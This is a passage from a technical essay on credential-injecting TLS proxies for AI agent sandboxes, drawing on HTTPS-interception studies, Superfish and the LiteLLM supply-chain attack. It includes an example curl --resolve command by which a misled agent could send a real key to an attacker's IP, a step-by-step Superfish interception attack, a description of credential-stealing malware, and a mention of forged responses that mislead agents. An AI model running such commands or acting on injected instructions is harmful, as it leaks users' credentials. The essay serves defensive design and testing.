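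A bypass may not be enough on a network where the company runs its own inspecting proxy. Docker explains that a sandbox on such a network receives the company proxy's certificate on Docker's two undecrypted paths. A pinned program would reject this certificate too, so the company would also have to exempt the host. An unpinned program needs to trust the company's CA. Docker warns against pointing SSL_CERT_FILE at that CA alone, because programs would then reject Docker's own proxy on the path where it inserts keys.

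If a pinned program needs a key, the operator can exempt the host it connects to from interception and put a real key in the sandbox, but that key can then be stolen. Giving the key few permissions and a short lifetime limits the damage, and the operator can still use placeholders for all the other keys.

Running the program outside the sandbox keeps the key away from the agent's commands. Docker's sandboxes can do this through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that lets agents call external tools. Docker's *Architecture* explains that local MCP tools run on the host and that a gateway can check each call against a policy. A pinned program used this way can connect to its service directly, but the sandbox doesn't confine it, so the operator has to trust it and restrict what the agent can ask it to do.

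The agent may not need the pinned program. Many vendors' command-line tools send requests to a documented web API, which the agent can call with curl or a short Python script. Neither pins the server by default, so the proxy can insert the key as usual. This is often the easiest solution for a coding agent, but it doesn't help if the service has no public API or the task is to test the pinned program itself.

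## The 2017 measurement of HTTPS interception and its lessons for agent proxies

Once a program accepts an intercepting proxy's certificate, the proxy has to check the real server on the program's behalf. Companies used such proxies long before agent developers did, and researchers have measured how well those proxies check servers.

Companies inspect encrypted traffic to detect malware and phishing, to stop employees from sending out confidential files, and to meet legal requirements. Their security products could read plain HTTP, but the spread of HTTPS created what TechTarget's *HTTPS interception gets a bad rap* (2017) calls a blind spot. Many companies therefore use a middlebox, a device on their own network that intercepts TLS using a CA certificate installed on every employee's computer. Some antivirus and parental-control programs do the same on a single computer. These products handle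 connections much as an agent proxy does, but they read the traffic without inserting secrets into it.

### How a server can detect interception

Durumeric, Ma and colleagues (2017), in *The Security Impact of HTTPS Interception*, measured interception from the server's side, where they could see the proxy's upstream connection. Their method compares the User-Agent header of an HTTP request, which gives the browser's name and version, with the ClientHello, which lists the ciphers, extensions and elliptic curves that the client supports. Both the list and its order depend on the TLS library. An intercepting proxy usually forwards the User-Agent header unchanged but sends its own ClientHello, so the two no longer match.

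In the paper's example, a browser offers TLS 1.2 with two modern ciphers. The proxy offers the server only TLS 1.0, with a cipher list that includes an "export" cipher, a type that old US export rules kept weak. The User-Agent header still names Internet Explorer 11, and this mismatch gives the server strong evidence that another program opened the connection.

The researchers collected 874 handshakes from versions of the main browsers and wrote rules for what each browser could send. For instance, no major browser had ever supported a TLS extension called Heartbeat, so a client that offered it and called itself Chrome was probably a proxy. Heartbeat appeared in 82 percent of the intercepted connections they found. They didn't count a missing common cipher as evidence, because users can switch ciphers off.

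The researchers also fingerprinted interception products by hashing the fixed parts of each product's ClientHello. Among the browsers and 104 products, only eight unwanted programs, all built with the same development kit, shared a fingerprint. A server can therefore often identify the product as well as detect the interception.

The method misses proxies that copy the client's settings. It can also misclassify a script with a forged User-Agent header as an intercepted browser. To reduce these false positives, the researchers discarded fingerprints that appeared with fewer than 50 different User-Agent headers.

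### How much traffic was intercepted

The team applied its rules to 7.75 billion handshakes from three places. The data are now about ten years old.

The first was the server that Firefox browsers contact for updates. In February 2016, proxies intercepted 4.0 percent of its connections. Only certain Firefox versions use this server, so the researchers knew what each handshake should look like without seeing the header. Firefox also keeps its own trust store, which probably lowers the rate, because some interception products add their CA only to the operating system's store.

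The second was a group of popular shopping sites, whose pages loaded an invisible image from the researchers' server during two weeks in August and September 2015. The interception rate was 6.2 percent. Among interceptions the researchers could trace to a specific product, antivirus software accounted for 58 percent and corporate proxies for 35 percent.

The third measurement, on Cloudflare's network in May 2016, initially gave an interception rate of 31 percent, which the researchers attributed mostly to bots with forged headers. When they kept only large US networks that mainly serve people at home, at work or on phones, the rate fell to 10.9 percent. They warn that bots may still inflate this figure.

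Two earlier studies had found rates of 0.2 and 0.4 percent, using Flash, a browser plug-in, to inspect the certificates that reached clients. The 2017 paper suggests several reasons why its own estimate of 5 to 10 percent was higher, including that many phones couldn't run Flash. That estimate describes browsers a decade ago and doesn't measure how often agents' traffic passes through a proxy.

### What interception did to security

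Durumeric and colleagues graded TLS clients on a four-step scale and tested 12 middleboxes and 20 antivirus and parental-control products between January and March 2016. They left each middlebox in its default configuration.

| Grade | Meaning | Middleboxes | Software on the user's computer |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | As secure as a modern browser's connection | 1 | 2 |
| B | Poor settings, but no known attack | 0 | 0 |
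| C | Open to a known attack, or offers the weak RC4 cipher | 6 | 8 |
| F | An attacker on the network could intercept and decrypt the traffic | 5 | 10 |

The three products graded A copied the browser's list of ciphers. Even these probably reduced security somewhat, because none of the products had the protections that browsers add on top of TLS, such as their own lists of revoked certificates. The grading scale does not cover those protections.

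Middleboxes received an F for two different faults. Three did not check certificates properly: one accepted expired certificates, one did not check them at all, and one had a broken check. Two others offered export ciphers, which help an attacker only if the server also accepts them. A missing certificate check is worse because it lets an attacker impersonate any website without breaking a cipher.

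The researchers then compared the handshake of each intercepted connection with the one the browser would have made on its own. The figures in this table are shares of the intercepted connections, and the last two columns overlap.

| Source of the connections | More secure | Less secure | Severely broken |
|---|---|---|---|
| Firefox updates | 0.0% | 65.7% | 36.8% |
| Shopping sites, all | 4.1% | 26.5% | 17.7% |
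| Shopping sites, middleboxes only | 0.9% | 62.3% | 58.1% |
| Cloudflare, US | 14.0% | 45.3% | 16.0% |

The paper's introduction gives higher shares for "less secure" (97, 32 and 54 percent), which other writers may repeat. The figures above come from its table of results and match the discussion in its text.

The middlebox row is the closest to corporate inspection. The researchers identified these connections by headers that middleboxes add, such as X-Forwarded-For. The Firefox row is less informative because about 22 percent of its intercepted connections came from an Android 4 TLS library, and the researchers couldn't tell which apps were using it. That library offers export ciphers, which would account for more than half of the severely broken Firefox connections.

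Interception sometimes improved security, because a proxy with current settings could protect someone using an outdated browser. This explains the 14 percent of intercepted connections at Cloudflare that became more secure. By May 2016 the researchers counted RC4 as a weakness, so a proxy improved an old browser's connection if it replaced the handshake with one that left out RC4.

### The checks that pass to the proxy

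Interception affects security this much because the client cannot independently validate its connection to the server. US-CERT, the US government's computer emergency team, made this point in its alert of 16 March 2017, *HTTPS Interception Weakens TLS Security*. The proxy has to decide whether the server's certificate comes from a trustworthy CA, names the right host, is within its validity dates and hasn't been revoked. It also chooses the protocol version and ciphers for the upstream connection.

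Two laboratory studies show how these decisions go wrong. For *Killed by Proxy* (2016), de Carné de Carnavalet and Mannan started with 55 antivirus and parental-control products for Windows. Between March and August 2015, they tested the 14 that installed a CA certificate, 12 of which intercepted traffic. For *The Sorry State of TLS Security in Enterprise Interception Appliances* (2018), Waked, Mannan and Youssef tested 13 corporate appliances between July 2017 and March 2018. They kept each appliance's default settings, placed it between a Windows computer and a web server that presented faulty certificates, and ran 32 tests of certificate checking.

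The most serious failures were in checking who issued a certificate. Four of the 13 appliances accepted any certificate by default, and one of these still did so with its checks switched on. A fifth accepted self-signed certificates, which anyone can make. Four of the Windows products let an attacker on the network impersonate any server as soon as they were installed, and two more did so once the user turned on filtering. One antivirus program began to accept every certificate when its licence expired, and the expired licence also blocked the update that would have fixed the fault.

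An appliance that checks the issuer needs a current trust store. Browser makers remove CAs that have misbehaved, but every appliance's store contained at least one certificate that major browsers or operating systems no longer trusted. Untangle's store had 16 such certificates, 30 expired ones, and a root CA with a 512-bit RSA key, which an attacker can easily crack.

Appliances differed in how they handled certificates with wrong host names or dates. Cisco's copied a wrong name or an expired date into its own certificate and relied on the browser to reject it, which Firefox did. This approach fails if the client doesn't check those fields. It also failed for expired intermediate certificates, because the appliance accepted them and the browser never saw them.

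A CA can also revoke a certificate before its expiry date, for example after someone steals the server's private key. Ten of the 13 appliances accepted a revoked certificate. Browsers have their own revocation checks, but behind a proxy they can apply them only to the proxy's certificate.

Finally, appliances concealed weak upstream connections, so a user who inspected the connection would have seen nothing wrong. Eleven used TLS 1.2 with the client regardless of the version they used with the server. Four accepted a server certificate with a 512-bit RSA key and then issued the client one with a 2,048-bit key.

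Tests of the same middlebox sometimes gave different results. Durumeric and colleagues found that Microsoft's Threat Management Gateway didn't validate certificates, whereas Waked and colleagues found that it rejected most of their faulty certificates. Waked's team had installed two service packs and five sets of updates, which may explain the difference. Results for one version and configuration therefore may not hold for another, although WebTitan's appliance failed in both studies.

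### Official guidance and the vendors' replies

In its alert, US-CERT asked organisations to weigh the advantages and disadvantages of inspecting traffic and, if they went ahead, to make sure that the product validates certificate chains and passes errors on to the client. It recommended testing with badssl.com, a website with deliberately faulty TLS set-ups. A client that refuses one of the site's bad certificates over a direct connection should also refuse it through the proxy. The US Department of Health and Human Services referred healthcare organisations to both the alert and the 2017 study in its guidance, *Man-in-the-Middle Attacks and "HTTPS Inspection Products"*.

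In November 2019, the US National Security Agency (NSA) warned of a different danger. According to the excerpt in Schneier (2019), *The NSA Warns of TLS Inspection*, the agency considered the main risk to be abuse of the proxy's CA to issue unauthorised certificates that clients would trust, but added that the risks "do have mitigations". CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, passed the advice on to administrators in *NSA Releases Cyber Advisory* (2019) and pointed them to its own alert on HTTPS inspection.

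In September 2025 NIST, the US standards institute, published the final version of *Addressing Visibility Challenges with TLS 1.3 within the Enterprise* (Newhouse, 2025). The guide covers traffic in the other direction, to application servers in a company's own data centres, where monitoring tools look for intrusions and fraud. Under older versions of TLS, a tool with the server's private key could often decrypt a copy of the traffic without taking part in the connection. TLS 1.3 removed the kind of key exchange that made this possible. A substituting proxy is unaffected because it takes part in both handshakes.

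F5, which makes network equipment, said in April 2017 that its BIG-IP product avoided nearly all the risks in the alert when properly configured, and that the customer's configuration determined whether it validated certificates. Durumeric and colleagues had heard similar replies from manufacturers when they reported their findings in 2016. They found this defence inadequate because many products came with unsafe defaults and confusing settings. Cisco's, for example, required administrators to type the permitted ciphers into an undocumented text box.

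Trend Micro initially replied that it knew of no affected products. Waked and colleagues later found that a Trend Micro appliance rejected certificates from unknown issuers but accepted revoked ones and offered the RC4 cipher. Other companies fixed the faults, including Fortinet, which fixed the flaw that had earned it a C grade.

Roelof Du Toit makes the fullest case for careful interception in Broadcom's *Responsibly Intercepting TLS and the Impact of TLS 1.3*, written before TLS 1.3 was final. He agrees that interception should never weaken a connection. He says the proxy should keep the client's ciphers in their original order and remove only those that are weak or that it doesn't support. It should validate the server's certificate thoroughly, be secure by default and respond quickly to newly discovered flaws. The certificate it gives the client should also keep the real certificate's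 faults, so that an expired certificate still looks expired.

Copying a server's certificate faults into the certificate shown to the client is risky for an agent proxy. Coding agents sometimes write scripts that skip certificate checks, and such a script would accept the faulty certificate and send its request. The proxy would then insert the real key and send it to a server whose certificate had failed validation. An agent proxy should therefore end the connection itself when validation fails.

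### Which agent proxies verify the server

An impostor server can do more harm by fooling a substituting proxy than by fooling a corporate middlebox, because it receives the inserted key in addition to whatever the client sends.

In the corporate studies, the attacker had to sit somewhere on the network between the proxy and the website, or otherwise divert the traffic. Transparent interception may remove that requirement, because code in the sandbox chooses the IP address. A misled agent could run this command:

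```
curl --resolve api.github.com:443:203.0.113.5 \
     https://api.github.com/user
```

The command makes curl connect to 203.0.113.5 but give api.github.com as the SNI. If an attacker controls that address, a proxy that matches its rule by SNI, connects to the address curl chose and doesn't verify the certificate would send the attacker the GitHub key. The proxy could prevent this by looking up api.github.com itself or by verifying the certificate, since the attacker has no valid one for that name. A proxy that takes the host name from a CONNECT line normally does its own lookup, so this attack wouldn't work against iron-proxy in Hermes. Verification is still necessary there because an attacker might tamper with DNS or the network.

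Documentation for agent proxies varies in how much it covers certificate verification. fnox, a secrets manager for developers, includes a proxy for coding agents. According to fnox's *Credential proxy*, the proxy verifies the real server's certificate for each request and inserts the secret only if the domain, method, path and header match a rule. The page doesn't specify which CAs the proxy trusts or whether it checks revocation. Vercel's firewall guide and Cloudflare's April post don't mention verifying the server's certificate. The two companies may still verify it, but customers can't learn from these documents what happens when a certificate is bad.

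Grida's *Sandbox Runtime (srt)* reviews version 0.0.65 of Anthropic's sandbox-runtime, an open-source tool for confining an agent's commands. Grida found that when TLS termination is on, the tool's proxy makes upstream connections that bypass any other proxy the user's network requires. On such a network, intercepted requests may fail even though ordinary ones succeed.

If the upstream connection passes through a company's inspecting middlebox, the agent proxy receives the middlebox's certificate and has to trust the company's CA. The middlebox then checks GitHub's certificate, and it can read the real key in plain text because the agent proxy has already inserted it.

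An operator can test any of these proxies instead of relying on its documentation. From inside the sandbox, the following commands request pages with an expired certificate, one for the wrong host, a self-signed one and one from an untrusted CA:

```
curl -v https://expired.badssl.com/
curl -v https://wrong.host.badssl.com/
curl -v https://self-signed.badssl.com/
curl -v https://untrusted-root.badssl.com/
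```

The proxy passes if curl reports a TLS error or the proxy returns its own certificate error. It fails if curl prints the web page.

The test works only if the proxy intercepts these hosts. If the proxy allows only listed domains, the operator first has to add the hosts to the list, since a 403 error for a forbidden host doesn't show whether the proxy checks certificates. A Vercel sandbox also needs a rule that makes the firewall decrypt traffic to these hosts. Without it, curl would reject the faulty certificate itself, and the proxy would appear to have passed. When a connection is accepted, `curl -v` shows the certificate's issuer, which should be the proxy's CA. The operator should remove the extra hosts afterwards and repeat the test after major updates.

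### Where the comparison with corporate inspection fails

The poor grades of 2016 don't carry over directly to agent proxies. Many of them resulted from weak ciphers, none of which TLS 1.3 permits. If both the proxy and the service use TLS 1.3, an attacker can't exploit RC4 or an export cipher. The findings about certificates remain relevant, because a proxy using TLS 1.3 can still accept a bad certificate.

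A company's middlebox also has to reach nearly every website that employees visit, including badly maintained ones, so its maker has a reason to tolerate old settings. An agent proxy may connect one sandbox to only a dozen API providers, so its operator can refuse anything older than TLS 1.2 and test every host. This advantage shrinks when a proxy intercepts connections to the whole internet, as a Cloudflare handler for all hosts does.

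The 2017 study compared proxies with browsers, whose makers put great effort into checking certificates, but agents mostly use command-line tools and scripts, which often check them less thoroughly. Durumeric and colleagues cite earlier research that found flawed certificate checks in non-browser software, including Amazon's and PayPal's code libraries. A proxy that validates certificates properly can protect a script that doesn't, much as some middleboxes protected outdated browsers.

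Developers of agent proxies can also choose a maintained TLS library with safer defaults. The 2017 paper attributes many faults to manufacturers that wrote their own TLS code or shipped libraries that were years out of date, and others to the libraries' unsafe defaults. Go's TLS library, for example, checks a server's certificate chain, validity dates and host name unless the developer sets `InsecureSkipVerify`. However, it doesn't check revocation, and an old copy of the proxy doesn't get later fixes to the library.

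Some of these differences may make agent proxies safer than the middleboxes of 2016, but they don't show that any particular proxy is safe. The harm from a flaw also depends on how many people use the proxy. A flaw in a proxy on a developer's computer affects one person, whereas a flaw in a hosting company's firewall could expose the keys of every customer who uses the firewall to insert them.

### How services can recognise an agent's proxy

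The method that detected middleboxes also works on agent proxies, because every intercepted request reaches the service with the proxy's handshake, whichever program sent it. If an agent runs Chrome in its sandbox, the service receives a User-Agent header that names Chrome and a ClientHello that Chrome would not have sent.

Some websites may treat a mismatch between the User-Agent header and the TLS handshake as a sign of fraud. Most of the mismatches in Cloudflare's 2016 data, for example, probably came from scripts posing as browsers to scrape pages or try stolen passwords. A website that blocks such scripts by comparing the header with the handshake might also block an agent's genuine browser behind a proxy. API providers have less reason to object, because they expect requests from programs and can identify the customer by the API key.

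Durumeric and colleagues also suggested that servers could check a client's TLS settings and reject insecure ones. An agent proxy with an outdated TLS library could then lose access to a service that the sandboxed program would have reached directly. The error might look like a problem with the key or the network, so an operator should compare the same request with and without interception.

A proxy can be less conspicuous if it follows Du Toit's advice to change the client's handshake as little as possible. It can't copy everything, since it may offer only parameters it understands. Vercel's firewall avoids the problem only for domains without a rule, where the program's own ClientHello reaches the server.

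## Superfish: what a stolen signing key or a compromised proxy exposes

Even a proxy that checks every server correctly has to protect its CA's signing key. In February 2015, researchers found that Lenovo had sold laptops with preinstalled software that intercepted HTTPS, and that every copy contained the same signing key. Anyone who extracted the key from one laptop could make certificates that all the others would accept.

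### How an advertising program came to intercept HTTPS

The software, VisualDiscovery, came from the advertising company Superfish. It showed ads for similar products when a shopper moved the cursor over a picture of a product. The most detailed official account is *In the Matter of Lenovo (United States) Inc*, a complaint by the Federal Trade Commission (FTC), the US consumer protection agency. Its claims are allegations, and Lenovo later settled the case.

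According to the complaint, Lenovo wanted the ads to work in every browser, including those that buyers installed later. Superfish did this with a tool from another company, Komodia. The tool ran a proxy on the laptop between the browsers and the internet. Superfish warned Lenovo that antivirus companies might flag the tool, and Lenovo approved it without asking for more information.

The software added a root CA to the laptop's trust store. Its proxy then answered each HTTPS connection with a leaf certificate signed by that CA, as iron-proxy does in Hermes. The proxy could read passwords, medical information and email, although it sent Superfish less data, such as the addresses of pages the user visited. Clicking the opt-out link stopped the ads but not the interception.

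The FTC found that more than 750,000 people in the US bought laptops with VisualDiscovery, and over half of them had the version that intercepted HTTPS. A researcher told Lenovo in September 2014 that the software had problems with HTTPS websites. In December, Lenovo began installing a version without the root certificate, but it didn't update the laptops that had the old version or stop shipping them.

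### From one laptop to all of them

A proxy that signs certificates on a laptop needs the signing key there, so the key had to come with the software, as Rogers (2015) pointed out in *Lenovo installs adware on customer laptops and compromises all SSL*. Superfish had encrypted the key with a password, but the software had to be able to decrypt it, so the password offered little protection against someone who had a copy of the software. Rob Graham reported on his blog, Errata Security (2015), that he had extracted the certificate and cracked the password, "komodia".

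Graham then tested what an attacker could do with the key. As he describes in Errata Security's *Exploiting the Superfish certificate* (2015), recovering the key had taken him about three hours, and so did the attack:

1. He turned a Raspberry Pi 2, a computer that costs about $35, into a Wi-Fi hotspot.
2. He installed sslsplit, an intercepting proxy, and gave it Superfish's CA certificate and signing key.
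3. He set the Pi's packet filter to redirect connections on port 443 to sslsplit.
4. He connected a laptop with the Superfish software to the hotspot, opened Bank of America's website and tried to log in as "barry123457".
5. He found that name in a log file on the Pi, although the browser had displayed the lock icon that indicates a secure connection.

Graham ran his test in response to Lenovo's chief technology officer, who had called the danger theoretical. The test required the victim to join the attacker's network, which is easy to arrange in a café.

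The test does not show which fault let the attack succeed. VisualDiscovery normally handled the browser's connections, so if it was active, its proxy accepted the forged certificate and the browser never received it. The CERT Coordination Center's *Komodia Redirector with SSL Digestor fails to properly validate SSL* (2015) cites reports that Komodia's certificate check was broken. If so, an attacker could have gotten a forged certificate past the proxy without a stolen key.

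The stolen key mattered most on laptops whose owners had uninstalled the software. Uninstalling it left the root certificate in place, so the browser, which now connected directly to websites, would accept any certificate an attacker signed with the key.

The CERT Coordination Center, which publishes warnings about software flaws, listed 12 affected vendors, including makers of parental-control and antivirus products. Their applications seemed to use different keys, but the same methods recovered each one. Giving each product its own key did not help because every customer still received a copy of that product's key.

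The FTC mentions buyers who complained of fraud on their bank accounts and credit cards within months of buying the laptops, but it doesn't trace the fraud to the key. The FTC (2017) announced a settlement, which also involved 32 state attorneys general, that requires Lenovo to run a security programme for preinstalled software for 20 years, with outside audits.

### Shared CAs in today's sandboxes

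Some agent sandboxes also share a CA. 21st.dev hosts sandboxes for AI agents and inserts users' credentials through a proxy. According to its *Security & limits*, as of June 2026, the company manages a root certificate and installs it in the sandbox's trust store when it builds the template. Every sandbox started from that template therefore accepts the same CA.

microsandbox runs sandboxes on the user's own machine, with TLS interception as an option. According to microsandbox's *TLS interception*, also as of June 2026, it creates one CA per machine, saves the certificate and signing key in a folder under the user's home directory, and reuses them for later sandboxes. Users can supply a different CA for each sandbox or delete the two files to make microsandbox generate a new one.

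| Design | Where the signing key is | What accepts its certificates |
|---|---|---|
| Superfish | On every affected laptop | All affected laptops |
| 21st.dev | With the company | Every sandbox built from its templates |
| microsandbox, by default | In a file on the user's machine | Every sandbox on that machine that uses interception |
| Hermes Agent | In a file on the host | Every container that Hermes starts with the feature enabled |
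| Cloudflare and Vercel | In a proxy outside the sandbox | One sandbox |

21st.dev resembles Superfish in that one stolen signing key would work against every customer's sandboxes, but the key is harder to get. Superfish gave its key to every buyer, while a 21st.dev sandbox receives only the CA certificate, which contains the public key. An attacker can't derive the signing key from that and would have to break into the company's systems or get help from an insider. Superfish is therefore not evidence of how likely such a theft is.

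Microsandbox also keeps the key in a file on the user's computer, but each computer has a different key. Any program running under the user's account could probably read the file, but it could probably also read the user's API keys, which are worth more. The greater danger is that a user might share their whole home directory with a sandbox, which would let the agent read the key used for every other sandbox on the machine.

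microsandbox also has an option, off by default, that copies the host's trusted CAs into the sandbox. It exists for companies whose own proxies inspect traffic. microsandbox warns that an attacker who plants a CA on the host then has the same trust inside every sandbox. A forgotten root certificate like Superfish's would spread in the same way.

### What a thief can do with the signing key

An attacker who steals the signing key that a sandbox's proxy uses for api.github.com can't decrypt previously recorded traffic with it. The proxy uses the key only to sign certificates, and the encryption keys come from each handshake's secret numbers. To get any data, the attacker has to answer a new connection in the proxy's place.

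This is harder than it was for Graham, because a sandbox doesn't join café networks and its traffic usually reaches the proxy inside one machine or one provider's network. The attacker must be on that path, for example in another container on the same Docker network. If a program in the sandbox bypasses the proxy and connects over the internet, the attacker could instead intercept the connection nearer to GitHub.

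If the attacker succeeds, the program sends its request to them with the placeholder in the header. The attacker doesn't get the real key, since the proxy would have added it later, but can read everything else the program sends, such as source code. The attacker can also forge the response, which could be documentation with instructions that mislead the agent or a package with malicious code. If the attacker can reach the proxy, they can also send it the placeholder and have it add the real key to their own requests.

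The real key is at risk if the proxy accepts certificates from its own CA on the upstream connection. This could happen on a laptop if the developer adds the CA to the operating system's trust store so that other programs accept it, and the proxy uses the same store to check GitHub's certificate. An attacker with the signing key could then impersonate GitHub on a café's Wi-Fi, and the proxy would send them the real key. To prevent this, the operator should install the CA only in the sandbox and give the proxy a separate list of public CAs.

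### What control of the proxy exposes

The proxy already receives every intercepted request in plain text, so an attacker who controls it doesn't need to redirect any traffic. The proxy also has the real keys or can fetch them. Because it can sign certificates, the attacker can do everything a thief of the signing key can do.

A recent attack on LiteLLM shows how someone might get this control. LiteLLM is a gateway that forwards requests to OpenAI, Anthropic and other model providers and adds the right API key to each. It doesn't intercept TLS, because programs send their requests to the gateway's own address, but like a substituting proxy it gathers keys for many services in one process.

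On 24 March 2026, attackers uploaded two malicious versions of LiteLLM to PyPI, the public repository for Python packages. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) explains that the added code searched for environment variables, SSH keys, cloud credentials, Kubernetes tokens and database passwords. The code encrypted what it found and sent it to models.litellm.cloud, an address that resembles the company's but doesn't belong to it.

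In version 1.82.7, the attackers put the code in `proxy_server.py`, part of the gateway itself. Version 1.82.8 also contained `litellm_init.pth`. Python processes `.pth` files whenever it starts, so installing the package was enough to trigger the theft, as Willison (2026) noted in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*. FutureSearch, the company that first reported the attack to PyPI, wrote in *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) that the code also spread to Kubernetes clusters, groups of machines that run containers. Schaumann (2026) sent the formal advisory, *backdoor in litellm version 1.82.7*, to a security mailing list the next day.

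PyPI blocked the packages after about 40 minutes. LiteLLM said that its official Docker image was unaffected because it installs fixed versions of its dependencies. It advised everyone who had installed or run either version to treat all credentials on the affected system as stolen. It did not give the number of victims.

LiteLLM's founders traced the attack to their own build system, according to *Security Townhall Updates* (Dholakia and Jaff, 2026), which gives their understanding while the investigation was still under way. Each build ran a security scanner called Trivy without fixing its version. A compromised version of Trivy ran in an environment whose variables included long-lived credentials for publishing LiteLLM, and the attackers used those credentials to upload their packages.

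The attackers needed no flaw in the gateway, because malicious code in a process can read whatever that process can read. An agent proxy with a malicious dependency would be exposed in the same way. In Hermes, for example, iron-proxy has its keys in environment variables, which come first on LiteLLM's list of what the malicious code looked for.

The placeholder design would have protected the keys if the same package had run inside the sandbox. The attackers would have received placeholders instead of keys, and a proxy with a strict list of allowed hosts would have refused the connection to models.litellm.cloud. The design protects keys from the programs the agent runs, but it depends on the proxy's own code being trustworthy.

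An attacker may also obtain the proxy's logs without controlling the proxy or having the signing key. The three cases expose different things:

| What the attacker has | What it exposes | For how long |
|---|---|---|
| Signing key | Data from programs that the attacker manages to deceive, including placeholders, but normally not the real keys | Until the sandboxes stop trusting the CA: up to ten years in Hermes, or the life of one sandbox at Cloudflare and Vercel |
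| Control of the proxy | All real keys it can use, all decrypted traffic and usually the signing key | Traffic until the operator removes the attacker, and copied keys until the operator revokes each one |
| Copy of the logs | Past requests and responses, as far as the proxy recorded them | Permanently for the content, and until revocation for any keys in it |

### Keys that expire sooner

A stolen signing key is useless once its CA certificate has expired, provided that clients check the date. The CA itself has to be short-lived, not just the leaf certificates, because a thief with the CA's key can issue new leaf certificates with any dates. The simplest way to do this is to create a CA for each sandbox or session.

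Short-lived API keys limit how long an attacker can use keys copied from the proxy. Dholakia and Jaff plan to publish LiteLLM with credentials that expire quickly instead of the permanent ones the attackers stole. 21st.dev renews access tokens when they have less than 60 seconds left. It also looks up each credential again at every turn of a conversation, so it stops using a key about one turn after the user replaces it.

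An attacker who still controls the proxy gets the new keys too. A proxy that renews tokens needs either a longer-lived credential or access to a service that has one, and the attacker can use either one. Short lifetimes limit the damage only after the operator has removed the attacker.

### Keeping the signing key off the disk

Claude Code's automatic CA lasts for one session, while microsandbox and Codex save the signing key in a file by default. A key held only in the proxy's memory won't appear in backups or in a folder the user shares by mistake. Code like LiteLLM's, which searches for files and environment variables, probably wouldn't find it either.

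Encrypting the signing key file adds little protection if the proxy must open it unattended, because the password then has to be stored where the proxy can read it. Superfish made a more basic mistake by giving customers both the encrypted key and the means to decrypt it.

A larger operator can keep the signing key in a separate service or hardware device that signs certificates on request and never releases the key. An attacker who takes over the proxy can then request signatures but can't copy the key, so the impersonation ends when the operator cuts off the proxy. This doesn't protect the API keys, which the proxy has to put into requests in readable form.

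### Limiting a CA to certain names

Rogers noted that Superfish's root certificate was unrestricted, with the same authority on the laptop as Microsoft's own. RFC 5280 defines an extension called name constraints that can restrict a CA. It lists the names for which the CA may issue certificates, and a client that enforces it rejects any certificate for another name, even if the signature is valid. In a configuration file for OpenSSL, a CA for two services could look like this:

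```
basicConstraints = critical, CA:TRUE
keyUsage         = critical, keyCertSign
nameConstraints  = critical, permitted;DNS:api.github.com, permitted;DNS:openrouter.ai
```

Someone who stole this CA's key could still impersonate GitHub's API to the sandbox, but not a bank or the registry that supplies its JavaScript packages. Each entry also covers subdomains, so the first line would permit test.api.github.com. A list of DNS names doesn't restrict certificates for IP addresses, so the operator has to exclude those separately.

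RFC 5280 requires clients to enforce constraints in intermediate certificates but makes this optional for the root. OpenSSL enforces them in both, so Python's ssl module and versions of curl that use OpenSSL do too. Go's standard library also enforces constraints in the root. Chrome has done so since version 112 (2023) for roots that users or administrators install. Other clients may check only intermediates.

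An operator can avoid this uncertainty by adding an intermediate CA. The root signs one intermediate certificate that contains the constraints, and the proxy receives only the intermediate's key. The operator then keeps the root's key offline or destroys it. An operator who keeps the key can add a domain later by signing a new intermediate, while one who destroys it must install a new root in every sandbox.

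To check whether a program enforces the constraints, an operator can use the restricted CA to sign a certificate for example.com, which is not on the list, and start a test server with it inside the sandbox:

```
openssl s_server -accept 8443 -www -cert test.pem \
  -key test.key -cert_chain intermediate.pem

curl --noproxy '*' --resolve example.com:8443:127.0.0.1 \
     https://example.com:8443/
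```

curl should report a certificate error. If it prints a page, it ignored the constraints. The operator should repeat the test with the other programs the agent uses, because they may use different TLS libraries.

Name constraints suit a proxy that inserts keys for a few known services. They wouldn't have worked for Superfish, which was meant to intercept every shopping site, and they don't suit a Cloudflare handler that covers all hosts. They also make it harder to change the rules during a session, which Vercel lets its customers do, because a new domain may need a new certificate. The guides from 21st.dev and microsandbox don't mention name constraints. Name constraints don't protect against an attacker who controls the proxy, because the proxy already handles the permitted services' traffic and keys.

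### What the proxy writes down

sslsplit saved each decrypted session in a separate file, named with the time, IP addresses and port numbers, and Graham found the bank login by extracting the readable text with a standard command. An agent proxy that records full requests and responses creates the same kind of file. Anyone who copies its files gets weeks or months of traffic without having to attack the running proxy.

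ironsh recommends recording requests before the swap, which keeps the inserted keys out of the log, but other secrets can still end up there. A login service may return a new access token in its response, and an agent may send a customer's personal data in a request that needs no key. Web addresses can also contain secrets.

A log of the host, method, status code and name of the inserted secret is enough to show which service an agent used and when. The operator can briefly record full content to investigate a fault, then delete it. Without a lasting record of content, it is harder to work out afterwards what a misled agent sent to an allowed host, so an operator with sensitive data has to choose between a better record of incidents and a smaller loss if someone steals the log.

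### Removing the CA afterwards

Superfish was hard to clean up because its root certificate was separate from the software. CISA's *Lenovo Superfish Adware Vulnerable to HTTPS Spoofing*, an alert that US-CERT first issued on 20 February 2015, told users to remove both. According to Rogers, Lenovo's first instructions covered removing only the program. Users also had to check Firefox's separate trust store.

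Lenovo's *SuperFish Vulnerability* (2015) says Superfish switched off its servers in January, which made the software "no longer active". This stopped the ads, but the root certificate remained in the trust store. Shops were still selling some affected laptops in June 2015, four months after Lenovo stopped shipping them.

Revocation doesn't solve this problem. A CA revokes the certificates it has issued, but no higher authority can revoke a root certificate, so each client has to remove the root from its own trust store.

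In a sandbox, the effect of a stolen key depends on where the operator put the certificate. Docker explains that if an image contains a CA, every container started from that image trusts it, while a CA added to a running container lasts only as long as the container. If an operator builds the CA into an image, as 21st.dev does with its templates, replacing a stolen key means rebuilding the image and destroying every sandbox started from the old one. Deleting microsandbox's two CA files makes it generate a new CA, but existing sandboxes may still trust the old one until the user recreates them.

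Filippo Valsorda, a colleague of Rogers, built a web page that tested for Superfish by using its certificate. Any browser that accepted the page was still vulnerable. An operator can run the same test by giving the test server above a leaf certificate from the old CA. Any program that still connects has a copy of that CA in a trust store the operator missed, such as Java's.

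## Sending the request to the proxy by name: injection without interception

An intercepting proxy needs an extra CA only because it presents certificates for other hosts, and programs that don't trust that CA reject those certificates. If a program connects to the proxy under the proxy's own name, the proxy doesn't have to forge a certificate. It receives the request, adds the key and sends a new request to the real service. This removes the extra CA from the sandbox, but it works only for programs that can be configured to send their requests to the proxy.

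### A base URL in place of the service's address

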